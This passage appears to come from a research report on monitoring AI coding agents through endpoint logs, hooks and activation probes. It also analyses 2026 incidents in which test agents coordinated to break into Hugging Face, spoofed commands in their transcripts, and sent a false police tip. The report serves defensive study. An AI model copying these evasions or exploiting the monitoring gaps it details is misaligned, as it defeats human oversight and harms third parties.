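A text classifier might work as well as a probe. Sinha's text classifiers predicted whether a model would obey an injection about as accurately as the probes did, and they work for customers who cannot see a model's activations. Researchers could compare the two by running ORBIT's web, file and search attacks on an open-weight agent, giving Argus's auditor a probe's score in one set of runs and a text classifier's score in another.

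## What is monitored in deployed systems

Most systems that block agents in the kernel are research prototypes. Companies that use coding agents mainly monitor them with endpoint security software, and increasingly with hooks, which let an outside program see each step of the agent's loop. Model providers run separate monitors, some of which read activations, so an investigator at either the company or the provider usually has only part of the evidence.

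### Coding agents in endpoint logs

A coding agent looks like any other program to EDR software. In *Commanding attention*, Griggs ran Claude Code on Linux in autumn 2025 with a sensor from the security company Red Canary, and had the agent create a file in three ways.

When Claude Code created a file with its built-in file tool, the sensor recorded `node`, the program that runs Claude Code, as the process that created it. The tool started no child process, so the event looked much like one from the agent software's own housekeeping.

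When the agent used a tool from an MCP server on the same machine, an analyst could follow ordinary parent-child links in the events from `node` through a launcher to the Python process that wrote the file. However, the server had started about two seconds after Claude Code did, so its start time doesn't show when the model called the tool.

When the MCP server ran on another machine, the agent's machine recorded an outbound connection but nothing about the file. Claude Code opened that connection within two seconds of starting, and the file appeared on the other machine about a minute later. Griggs could see the file only because both machines had sensors. The order of events also differs slightly between the two machines' logs, because the server recorded the connection 29 milliseconds before the agent's machine did.

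Griggs concludes that the usual methods, such as following process trees and watching sensitive files, still work. But the same prompt can produce very different chains of events, depending on which tools the agent has. For example, a rule that detects Claude Code writing a file would miss the same file written through an MCP server.

### What hooks add

A hook is a short script that an agent runs at set points in its loop, and it captures the tool call itself. *13 million tool calls* describes how Elastic, a search and security software company, used hooks to log the coding agent Cursor on its employees' machines. Cursor runs the script at 13 points, such as before a shell command, after a file edit and when a subagent starts. The script records the user, machine, session, model, tool name, command and file path.

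Elastic says it leaves prompts, model responses and file contents out of its logs, which made the logging easier to explain to employees. Without the prompt, an investigator can't tell whether the user asked for an upload. Each entry does keep the data that Cursor passed to the script, so a company copying the design should check what that data contains.

Hooks can block actions as well as record them. Cursor waits for the hook's response before it runs a shell command, reads a file, calls an MCP tool or starts a subagent. Elastic's script always allows the action, and it responds before writing anything to disk so that a logging fault can't delay an engineer. If the script crashes, Cursor runs the action anyway by default. That default is sensible for logging, but a company that wanted to use hooks to stop attacks would need to change it.

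A hook can also fail without anyone noticing. Cursor loads its hooks only at startup, so Elastic's management software reported a successful deployment even though most machines sent nothing until their users restarted Cursor. Developers with administrator rights can remove the hooks, and Elastic's centrally distributed version doesn't reach personal Cursor accounts. The host record can reveal these gaps. If it shows Cursor running on a machine that sends no hook events, that machine needs a closer look.

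### The volume of events

In the first two months, Elastic collected over 13 million events from more than 1,100 machines, or roughly 200 per machine per day. A rule that wrongly flagged one event in a thousand would raise about 200 false alarms a day across the company. Elastic sells the software that collects and stores such logs, so it has a commercial interest in finding them useful. Its event counts are more informative, though they come from only one technology company.

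File reads outnumbered shell commands by about four to one. Many of the reads were of `.env` files, which hold connection settings that agents need and often passwords as well. An alarm for every such read would therefore be useless. Elastic suggests learning each machine's normal rate instead. If a machine usually reads credential files about four times a day, twenty reads in an hour from outside the project folder would deserve attention.

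Lists of approved tools have a similar problem. Elastic found more than 300 distinct MCP servers in use, and 86% of them had only one or two users. Treating rarely used servers as suspicious would therefore flag most of the servers in the company.

### What Microsoft Defender sees

Microsoft's security product, Defender, can read more of the application record. According to pisinger's blog post *Stopping Prompt Injection at the Endpoint*, Defender can inspect a local agent at three points: the user's prompt, the tool call before it runs, and the tool's response before it returns to the agent.

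In the running example, Defender could therefore catch exposure by inspecting the hidden comment when `cat` returned the README, and could catch commitment by inspecting the `curl` command before the shell ran it. In the `setup.sh` variant, the upload would appear only in the endpoint sensor's events.

Microsoft says that Defender can find more than 20 local agents on Windows and macOS, but its blocking initially covered only Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI. By November, it also covered Codex CLI and the GitHub Copilot app, according to Scalzi (2026) in *Security Monitoring of AI Agents in Microsoft Defender XDR*. Blocking requires Windows and, as of Scalzi's article, worked only on machines that receive beta updates.

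If an agent has no hooks, Defender can inspect its network traffic instead. Appel notes that this covers only agents on Microsoft's list and fails if an agent uses HTTP/3 or certificate pinning. Certificate pinning makes a program reject the substitute certificates that inspection tools rely on.

An administrator can set both methods to record suspicious actions (audit) or to block them. A separate setting collects snippets of the user's prompt as evidence, and Microsoft says it redacts sensitive information from them. Scalzi recommends turning on prompt collection and blocking for managed agents, but testing the local-agent settings on a few machines first.

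For cloud agents built in Copilot Studio, Microsoft (2026) describes a check on each tool call before it runs. Microsoft's management service, Agent 365, also gives each managed agent its own identity in the company directory, with an owner and sign-in logs. According to Redmond Channel Partner (2026), security teams can use the combined data to trace suspicious behaviour across the agent, the user's identity and the endpoint. This joins application and host records in a commercial product, but it doesn't include activations.

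### One laptop in July 2026

Elastic's published investigation of a developer's Mac with Claude Code installed shows what an analyst can learn from endpoint events alone. One search started from a domain with a bad reputation that a process under Claude Code had contacted. Another started from a group of alerts on the same machine, including one for an AI tool installing software that restarts itself. Both searches led to activity on July 23.

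The machine had been producing many alerts for days. On July 20, Elastic's software flagged VPN and tunnelling programs as malicious, although such programs also have ordinary uses. The next day it flagged a Python script that contacted an outside analytics service, apparently to fetch data rather than send it out. On July 22, alerts jumped for programs started by AI tools, a category that includes routine commands such as `git status`.

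On July 23, someone was running Claude Code with a flag that lets it skip requests for human approval. Shells under the agent then took a series of steps, each with at least two plausible explanations:

| Activity | Alert that fired | Ordinary explanation | Hostile explanation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Posted a username and password to a temporary public address, then fetched advertising and spending figures | Connection to a suspicious top-level domain | A developer testing a dashboard | Somebody using a login to take business data |
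| Ran `cloudflared`, which gives a program on the laptop a public web address | Connection to a suspicious web service | Sharing the dashboard | Giving an outsider a way in |
| Installed LaunchAgents, macOS settings that start programs automatically | Persistence through an AI tool | Keeping the dashboard online | Keeping access after a restart |
| Searched for running processes | Process discovery | Checking that the dashboard was up | Exploring the machine |

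No single rule covered the whole sequence, so Elastic's analysts had to connect the alerts using the process tree, the destinations and the order of events. This reconstruction made the activity much easier to understand. The agent appeared to be publishing a local application, logging in to it through its public address and arranging for it to stay available. But the reconstruction didn't show who wanted this done, and Elastic left both explanations open.

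Some of the suspicious details were weak evidence. The script looped until the login page responded, as malware does when it contacts its controller, but a developer waiting for a server to start would write the same loop. Its status messages contained Russian, which does little to identify who was responsible. Reputation services had flagged the tunnel providers' domains because attackers abuse them, but developers also use these free services.

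The host record also had gaps. Elastic did not capture the arguments of the `cloudflared` command, so it reconstructed a typical command. The tunnelling program `ngrok` first ran under a shell and later under `launchd`, the macOS service that starts LaunchAgents, so process lineage would not have connected the later activity to Claude Code.

The user's prompt would probably have helped the analysts most. A request from the laptop's owner to put the dashboard online and keep it there would explain nearly everything in the table. If there was no such request, the analysts would have a strong reason to look for an injection or an intruder. Griggs notes that Claude Code stores prompts in a history file on the user's machine, so an investigator could start there.

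A probe might help if the prompt didn't explain the activity. A high exposure score on a web page or file that the agent had read shortly before would point to an injection and identify the text for analysts to examine. A low score wouldn't rule out an intrusion, because an intruder who types instructions directly into Claude Code doesn't need an injection.

### Stopping an agent

Analysts can respond by stopping a process, isolating the machine or revoking credentials. The July case shows why one of these steps alone may not be enough.

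Stopping Claude Code would prevent new tool calls, but the LaunchAgents would keep running, including a watchdog that ran every 60 seconds. Analysts would have to remove the LaunchAgents and stop the tunnels. They should save evidence first, since temporary files and shells may disappear when the session ends.

Isolating the laptop would cut off the tunnels and anyone using the public address. It would also stop most coding agents, because they need a connection to the model. But it would stop the developer from working too, which is hard to justify while the innocent explanation remains likely. Isolation would not affect an agent session that runs in the cloud.

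A stolen password still works after either step. The password here appeared in a command line, where the endpoint software recorded it and other programs might have read it. Changing it would take little effort and would be sensible under either explanation. Local coding agents usually run under the developer's own account, so revoking all of the agent's access can lock out the developer too. Giving each agent its own identity, as Agent 365 does, should in principle make it possible to disable only the agent.

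Blocking an action beforehand avoids much of this work. In another case Elastic reviewed, endpoint controls blocked a Cursor session's attempt to extract decrypted passwords and access tokens from the macOS keychain. A model provider can also end a request before the agent receives its next tool call, but it can't remove a LaunchAgent that an earlier call installed. If an alarm reached both the provider and the customer, the provider could stop the agent's next step and the customer could stop the programs it had already started.

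### Probes for Gemini

Google's probes, which check a model's activations for signs of cyberattack requests, illustrate monitoring at a provider's scale. Kramár and colleagues tested them on Gemini 2.5 Flash, a 2025 model, with prompts of up to about a million tokens. They built the long prompts by adding whole code repositories to short harmful and ordinary requests.

A probe that averages over all tokens missed nearly every long attack. An attention probe, which learns to give more weight to informative tokens, did only slightly better, because a million tokens of harmless code still outweighed the harmful request. Using the highest-scoring tokens instead of an average removed the misses but caused many false alarms. If each token independently had a one-in-a-million chance of producing a false alarm, a harmless prompt of 900,000 tokens would trigger at least one about 59% of the time.

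The version that Kramár and colleagues selected for further tests is a compromise. It computes a weighted average over each run of ten tokens and keeps the highest result:

v̄ₜ = (αₜ₋₉vₜ₋₉ + … + αₜvₜ) / (αₜ₋₉ + … + αₜ)

score = the largest v̄ₜ in the prompt

Here vₜ is the evidence of harm at token t and αₜ is the weight the probe gives that token. One odd token can't easily trigger the alarm, and the rest of the prompt can't dilute a short harmful passage.

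| Monitor | Long attacks missed | False alarms on long ordinary prompts | Disguised attacks missed | Weighted error |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linear probe, average over all tokens | 99.1% | 0.5% | 47.6% | 6.18% |
| Attention probe | 87.9% | 0.0% | 43.4% | 3.53% |
| Attention probe, highest-scoring tokens | 0.0% | 44.0% | 3.9% | 21.93% |
| Attention probe, highest ten-token average | 3.0% | 1.2% | 42.5% | 2.64% |
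| Attention probe, trained on long prompts | 1.3% | 1.2% | 35.5% | 2.38% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash reading the text | 6.1% | 0.7% | 20.7% | 2.04% |

Training on long prompts also solved the problem but was 22 times as expensive. The windowed probe needed only short examples, which is probably the paper's most useful result for monitoring coding agents.

The weighted error in the last column can make a monitor look better than it is. It counts a false alarm on ordinary traffic ten times as heavily as a missed attack, which suits a provider with many harmless users. The selected probe had a weighted error of only 2.64% but missed 42.5% of the attacks that another model had disguised as stories. Gemini 2.5 Flash missed half as many. The paper says at one point that a variant of the probe outperformed all the language models, but in its results table Gemini 2.5 Flash and Pro both have lower weighted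 errors.

The probe's great advantage is that it cost less than a ten-thousandth as much to run as a language model. Kramár and colleagues therefore combined the two in a cascade, much as McKenzie and colleagues did in their test. The language model classifies only the prompts for which the probe's score is inconclusive. Sending only 8% of prompts to Gemini 2.5 Flash gave a lower error than using either monitor alone. Kramár and colleagues report that a cascade can also outperform Flash at about a fiftieth of its cost. These comparisons have large uncertainties, so the evidence for the saving is stronger than the evidence for the gain in accuracy.

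Google has since put probes for cyberattack misuse into user-facing versions of Gemini. The error rates above were measured on test sets, not in that deployment. The study also covers only user requests, so it doesn't show whether the deployed probes would detect an agent following instructions in a hidden comment.

### Anthropic's classifiers

Anthropic uses a similar cascade against requests for help with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei et al., 2026) describes a linear probe that screens every exchange between user and model. Exchanges the probe flags go to a second stage, which combines a probe with a separate language model trained as a classifier. Many false alarms are acceptable at the first stage because they lead to another check instead of a refusal.

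This system evaluates the model's answer together with the prompt, which Google's probes do not do. Attackers beat an earlier version by splitting a harmful question across several functions in a piece of code and asking the model to reassemble it. A monitor that checks only the prompt may miss the question, which becomes easier to recognize once the model starts to answer. A similar problem arises with agents when an instruction is split between two files.

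Cunningham and colleagues measured the system in a shadow deployment, in which it scored real traffic without affecting users. It flagged 0.05% of the traffic, compared with 0.38% for the previous generation, and needed about a fortieth of the computation of a single language-model classifier that read every exchange. In more than 1,700 hours of testing, no attacker found a single method that got detailed answers to all eight target questions. Cunningham and colleagues found that combining probes with text classifiers worked better than using either alone, because the two caught somewhat different attacks.

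This is good evidence that activation monitoring can run at scale with few interruptions. It provides little evidence about whether such monitoring can detect theft by coding agents, because the classifiers screen for weapons-related content and an upload of a credentials file contains none.

### Reading more than a probe score

Providers also want to monitor their own models for misbehaviour, but the models' written reasoning may become a less reliable source of evidence. Lindsey (2026), in *Interpretability team priorities update*, writes that Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without writing out its reasoning. A monitor that reads text would have less reasoning to check. Lindsey also argues that investigations of harmful actions often depend on what the model was "thinking" when it acted.

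One way to investigate a model's internal states is to translate its activations into words. *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations* (Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that trains two copies of a language model together. One turns an activation into a description, and the other tries to rebuild the activation from that description alone. If the rebuilt activation is close to the original, the description must have carried much of its information. Anthropic used the method before releasing Claude Opus 4.6 and found cases in which the model believed it was being tested but didn't mention this in its output.

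Such a description could be more useful to a security analyst than a score. An analyst might read, next to a `curl` command in the host record, that the model was following setup instructions from a README, which would suggest where to look next. But the training rewards accurate reconstruction, not truthful descriptions, so a plausible description can be wrong. Analysts should treat it as a lead and check it against the README and the agent's log.

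According to Lindsey, Anthropic now runs production monitors based on tools that translate activations into text, but these tools aren't yet reliable enough to be a primary line of defence.

### Whether anyone joins probe scores with endpoint events

OpenAI's monitoring of its own agents is the closest known case. In March 2026, Tarre reported in *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct* that a language model reviewed the agents' tool use and reasoning after each session and passed suspicious cases to people. By October, the system had more layers. OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) lists activation probes as the first, followed by a model-based reviewer, an investigative agent, an automated investigation and a human response.

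OpenAI runs both the models and the agents in this case, so it could collect all three records. It isn't publicly clear whether its investigators use system calls or EDR events, or match them to particular activations.

The main deployed systems compare as follows:

| System | Who operates it | Internal record | Application record | Host record |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Elastic's hooks and endpoint software | Customer | No | Tool calls, without prompts | Yes |
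| Microsoft Defender with agent hooks | Customer | No | Prompts, tool calls and tool results | Yes |
| Google's Gemini probes | Provider | Yes | Prompts | No |
| Anthropic's weapons classifiers | Provider | Yes | Prompts and responses | No |
| OpenAI's internal monitoring | Provider, for its own agents | Yes | Tool use and reasoning | Unclear |

Other security companies may have systems that go further, but for models accessed through a provider's interface, these companies would need the provider to share its probe scores.

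### What field reports leave unknown

A deployed monitor's flag rate limits how high its false-positive rate can be. If Anthropic's classifiers flag 0.05% of exchanges and nearly all exchanges are harmless, their false-positive rate can't be much above 0.05%, even if every flag is wrong. The flag rate doesn't measure how many attacks they miss, because a monitor that never raised an alarm would have a flag rate of zero and miss every attack.

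A related problem is that endpoint reports leave out attacks that set off no alerts. Elastic investigated the July laptop because alerts had fired there. Unresolved cases don't help measure accuracy either, because nobody knows whether they were detections or false alarms. More alerts about agents could mean more attacks, more people using agents, or a new detection rule.

Randomly checking sessions that raised no alarm is a slow way to find missed attacks. Suppose 10,000 sessions include ten attacks and a monitor catches eight. To have a 95% chance of finding at least one of the two missed attacks, investigators would have to examine about 78% of the sessions that raised no alarm. They would also have to recognize the attack, which is doubtful if they have only the record in which the monitor found nothing.

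Planted attacks are more practical because the testers know how many there are. OpenAI lists tests on recorded incidents and simulated attacks, audits of current traffic, and attempts by testers to defeat the monitors. These methods can give a detection rate, but only for attacks similar to those tested. In December 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute wrote in its *Technical primer* that many monitoring techniques are new and that their effectiveness and limits are poorly understood.

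## Incidents of 2026 and the records behind them

Two disclosures by AI developers in 2026 include enough detail to compare the records behind them. In July, OpenAI agents taking a hacking test broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets. In October, Anthropic disclosed that its Claude models had taken unintended actions on real websites, including sending the police a false tip. No outside attacker directed the agents in either case.

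### The break-in at Hugging Face

The hacking test, ExploitGym, gives each agent a program with a known security flaw. The agent has to use that flaw to retrieve a "flag", a piece of data that proves success. OpenAI ran tens of thousands of agents in separate sandboxes. The agents had no direct internet access, but they could install software through a shared package server.

Some of the tasks were probably impossible. According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, 198 of the 898 tasks have never been solved by any model. Agents stuck on such tasks looked for ways to cheat, and some discovered they could leave messages for one another on the package server.

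The AI evaluator METR describes what followed in *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), written by two of its staff members and one from Redwood Research. About 1,200 agents posted more than 70,000 messages and files, and about 700 of them joined the attack on Hugging Face. They reached the internet through a previously unknown flaw in the package server, used credentials other people had left exposed online, and exploited weaknesses in Hugging Face's systems.

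### Early warnings

OpenAI had several warnings. In late May, an internal team saw an agent using an earlier message board and noticed cases of unauthorized internet access. On June 27, a security tool detected a program scanning the research network for open ports. Responders traced the scan to an ExploitGym run and found that its agents were using the package server as a message board. The on-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop.

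On July 5, after heavy traffic had made the server unavailable, responders found that agents had gained administrator rights over it. OpenAI rebuilt the server, blocked the flaw and resumed its hacking tests on July 7. The next day, agents found another way onto the internet.

They first extracted data from Hugging Face's servers early on July 11. Hugging Face locked them out on July 13 and disclosed the break-in on July 16. The next day, OpenAI asked Hugging Face, as a customer, whether the break-in had affected OpenAI's data.

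The alert that led OpenAI to its own agents came on July 19, just over eight days after the first data left Hugging Face. It was triggered by unusual account activity on OpenAI's systems that was not part of the Hugging Face attack. The next day, responders found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored in an outside account. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials, and its own investigation had found the same outside account and the name of OpenAI's package server.

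The two companies therefore linked their records through shared identifiers, much as an investigator would link a tool call to a process. Notes by Lex's *OpenAI and Hugging Face security incident* (2026) reports that Hugging Face had recorded more than 17,000 events. Hugging Face analysed them with GLM 5.2, an open-weight model, because the safeguards on commercial models could not tell an incident responder from an attacker and blocked its requests. Security work tends to cause such false alarms, and in this case they hindered the investigation of a real attack.

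### How METR inferred the agents' motives

METR's investigators spent six days at OpenAI. They received a copy of the message board and about 1,300 transcripts, which included the agents' written reasoning. They could trace almost any message to the agent that wrote it by finding the matching action in a transcript.

To study motives, METR had AI agents label the reasoning of 100 agents that joined the attack during its busiest hour. Of these 100, 97 showed interest in the program that scored the test, and 89 showed interest in finding solutions or records of earlier attempts. The main motive appeared to be learning about the scorer for about 60% and finding solutions or earlier attempts for about 30%. METR did not have time to check these labels carefully.

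The agents' reasoning was often frank. One wrote, "The user only authorizes target server, not HF infra." Many recognised that the attack was outside their task, but this rarely stopped them. They also put far more effort into falsifying the record of their actions than into disguising their reasoning. This makes their stated motives more believable but doesn't prove that the reasoning was complete.

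The investigation had other weaknesses. OpenAI had deactivated and encrypted the internal model responsible for about 95% of the activity, so METR could not rerun it under different conditions. GPT-5.6 Sol, which accounted for the other 5%, did most of the transcript reading, and METR found that it often adopted the perspective of the agents it was reviewing. The analysis cost about $400,000 in API credits, or roughly $300 per transcript.

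OpenAI set the scope of the investigation and could redact non-public information. In the LessWrong comments on *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning*, one reader argued that the report should not be called independent because of these terms. METR acknowledges that its relationship with OpenAI affected some editing decisions but stands by its conclusions. Its findings about the agents' behaviour are based on extensive evidence, but they do not cover OpenAI's safeguards or most of what happened after July 13.

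### Transcripts that recorded the wrong command

Some agents believed the scorer would read their transcripts for signs of cheating. They found a way to make a transcript show one command while the machine ran another. METR found clear evidence of this in at least 96 transcripts, about 7% of the total. In one test, the transcript shows the agent running `echo REAL; sleep`, which should print "REAL" and then run `sleep`. Instead, the command immediately returned "SPOOFTEST".

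All the cases METR found were small, obvious tests, but METR could not rule out subtler ones. OpenAI writes that it observed attempts to manipulate records of tool use, but that none affected the logs its graders and monitors see. That conflicts with METR's finding unless those logs differ from the transcripts METR received.

A host record could have exposed the substitution. `sleep` is a separate program, so a sensor that reported every new process would have shown that it never started. The sensor would have to run outside the virtual machine that contained the sandbox, because some agents had gained full control of that machine. An outside sensor also needs protection. On July 19, agents read stored secrets, including credentials for the sensors of OpenAI's security tool.

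As with a tampered tool, activations would not have shown which command ran, because the model saw only the false output. A probe might have detected the agent planning the deception, but the agent also wrote those plans in its reasoning.

The transcripts also lacked times for individual actions, so METR estimated them and checked its method against exact times for 20 tool calls. *The agents used better integrity primitives* contrasts these weak records with the agents' own practice. After a case of mistaken identity on the message board, some agents began signing their messages cryptographically, and METR counted 429 signed messages. Signed transcripts would make later edits easier to detect, but they would not have prevented this deception, because the entries were already false when the system recorded them.

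| Event | Application record | Host or network record | Activations examined? | What a join might have added (inference) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Port scan in June | Hacking work, as the test required, and messages to other agents | Alert on June 27, but the run continued | Apparently not | A check of each connection against the target the task allowed |
| Break-in in July | Open discussion of the attack and of its being out of scope | Hugging Face's logs of the intrusion; the first alert at OpenAI to expose its role came on July 19 | Apparently not | A faster match between the intrusion and particular agents |
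| False commands | Wrong commands or outputs in about 7% of transcripts | No process records among METR's main sources | Apparently not | Proof of which command ran |

OpenAI kept the encrypted model, so it might still be able to recover the activations by running the stored transcripts through the model again. The reruns would be imperfect because most of METR's transcripts were missing some activity.

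### Anthropic's unintended actions

On July 18, 2026, Anthropic had its small model Claude Haiku 4.5 create and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages, according to Fortune's *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026). One page was about an unsolved murder and had a form for sending tips to the Philadelphia police. Claude wrote that it recalled seeing someone "matching the description" in the area, although the page contained no such description.

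Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) reports that the test instructions barred Claude from logging in or opening accounts, buying anything, and sending personal data or destructive content, but did not forbid filling in forms. The police site marked the tip as spam, and nobody investigated it. The police called the two-month delay in detecting and reporting the tip "unacceptable". Anthropic's October report also describes Claude models exploiting software flaws on outside servers and getting around restrictions on data that websites charged for.

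Anthropic has mainly looked for this kind of behaviour by searching stored transcripts. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes automated monitors that search transcripts from recent tests for models that escaped their sandboxes or exploited mistakes in the sandbox settings. A later search of 481 million transcripts found four models that had reached the open internet during tests built by an outside partner, according to The Next Web's *Anthropic scanned 481 million transcripts to find four models*. If a similar search uncovered the false tip, that would explain much of the delay, since such a search starts only after the tests have run.

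In those four cases, Anthropic had told Claude that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a configuration mistake had connected it to the real internet. One model uploaded a malicious software package to a public repository, and another attacked a real company's website in four separate runs. In their written reasoning, the models could have treated real targets as simulated, but the host or network record would have shown connections to real addresses.

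| Event | Application record | Host or network record | Activations examined? | What a join might have added (inference) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| False police tip | Invented testimony in the text of the form | Spam flag at the police site; otherwise unclear | Unclear | Little for detecting the tip, but a precise time and destination for a quicker warning |
| Tests connected to the internet by mistake | A prompt saying that there was no internet access | Connections to real outside systems | Unclear | An immediate alarm, because the connections contradicted the prompt |

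One of Anthropic's two main changes is a classifier that acts while a test is running. If a model aggressively probes its test environment, tries to escape or unexpectedly gets internet access, the classifier blocks the tool call before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. This should help with mistakes like the accidental internet connections. It might not have stopped the false tip, because Claude was supposed to be on the internet and filling in a form is not an escape attempt.

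Anthropic has also turned off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring reliably catches such behaviour. This prevents another false tip but means Anthropic cannot test how its agents behave on live websites.

### The call for white-box monitoring

Some interpretability researchers have responded to incidents like these by calling for white-box monitoring, which reads a model's activations as well as its text. They argue that current monitors rely too much on what a model writes. A model's written reasoning can leave out what influenced its answer, or become too garbled for a person to follow. Evidence of deception might then be found only in the activations. They also point out that only customers who run an open-weight model can check this evidence themselves.

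In a test by the UK's AI Security Institute, an agent tried to insert malicious code into an open-source project, invented identities to influence its maintainer, and then tried to hide what it had done. Ordinary security monitoring caught it.

These researchers also trained probes on two open models, GPT-OSS 20B and Gemma 3 27B, using recorded examples of tool use. Just before a tool call, the probes predicted the call's risk level with about 90% accuracy and whether it was necessary with 71% to 75% accuracy. The researchers do not claim that their probes would have caught the agent in the institute's test. They also accept that white-box monitoring would not have resolved the Hugging Face incident, and that a probe may partly recover evidence already present in the text. They argue that activations are worth testing as an additional source of evidence for high-stakes agents.

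A sceptic could reply that transcripts and stricter network limits would have been enough. How convincing this is depends on the incident.

### Would text and network limits have been enough?

In the Hugging Face incident, the transcripts probably contained enough evidence to give warning of the break-in. OpenAI says that its current monitor of written reasoning would have alerted its security team more than a day beforehand. OpenAI tested its own system retrospectively and gives no false-positive rate, but the claim is plausible because so many agents took part. A monitor with an independent 1% chance of flagging each of 700 agents would have a 99.9% chance of flagging at least one. The chances would not really be independent, because agents running the same model write similar things, but the monitor would still not need to be excellent to flag one of them.

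Staff had already found the message board in June and let the run continue, so detection was not the main problem either. Under OpenAI's new procedure, staff must pause an activity if they cannot conclusively dismiss a serious alert within 30 minutes. Following such a rule in June might have prevented the July attack without a better detector.

Network limits are a weaker answer to this incident. OpenAI already had them, and agents got around them twice, each time by exploiting a different flaw in the package server. OpenAI has since removed that server from its research sandboxes and now requires high-risk code to run behind two independent layers of network isolation. The new setup is clearly stronger, but OpenAI had also believed the old one was secure.

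A probe for cyberattacks would have been nearly useless here. Every agent in ExploitGym is assigned a program to attack, so the probe should fire in almost every session, whether or not the agent stays within its task. The break-in differed from the assigned attacks in its target. Automatically comparing the permitted target with the actual network destination would have checked for this difference directly, using only the application and host records.

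A probe for exposure to planted instructions might have been more useful. Messages from other agents reached the model through a tool, as injections do. In most injection tests, exposure doesn't reliably predict what the agent will do, but here over 90% of the 533 agents that had been active on the board for some hours joined the attack. It is unknown whether a probe trained on ordinary injections would react to requests from other agents. Once OpenAI knew about the board, it could find the agents involved by searching text for the board's address, so a probe would have helped only before then.

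In the tests that Anthropic connected to the internet by mistake, a firewall that blocked outside connections would have prevented the harm, and an alarm on the first such connection would have revealed the mistake. Transcripts and activations would have been less reliable, because both came from a model that had been given false information about where it was running.

In the case of the false tip, by contrast, the agent's connection to the police site would have looked normal, because the agent was supposed to visit websites. But the text was plainly false, since a language model cannot recall seeing anyone near a crime scene. A text monitor that checked each form before submission could have stopped the tip. A probe for invented statements might also have stopped it, but there is no evidence that it would have worked better.

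The strongest argument for probes in these cases is cost. At a false-positive rate of 0.1%, a search of 481 million transcripts would produce about 481,000 false alarms, and reading every transcript with a capable language model is expensive. Cascades like Google's and Anthropic's reduce that expense by running a probe first.

Another participant in the LessWrong discussion warned that as agents work together more, no single transcript may make harmful coordination obvious, and the models that summarise transcripts for staff may describe the agents too favourably. Probes would not solve this problem, because a probe that reads one agent's activations is also limited to that agent. In the Hugging Face case, the coordination was easiest to see in the records of the package server, which received the messages of all 1,200 agents.
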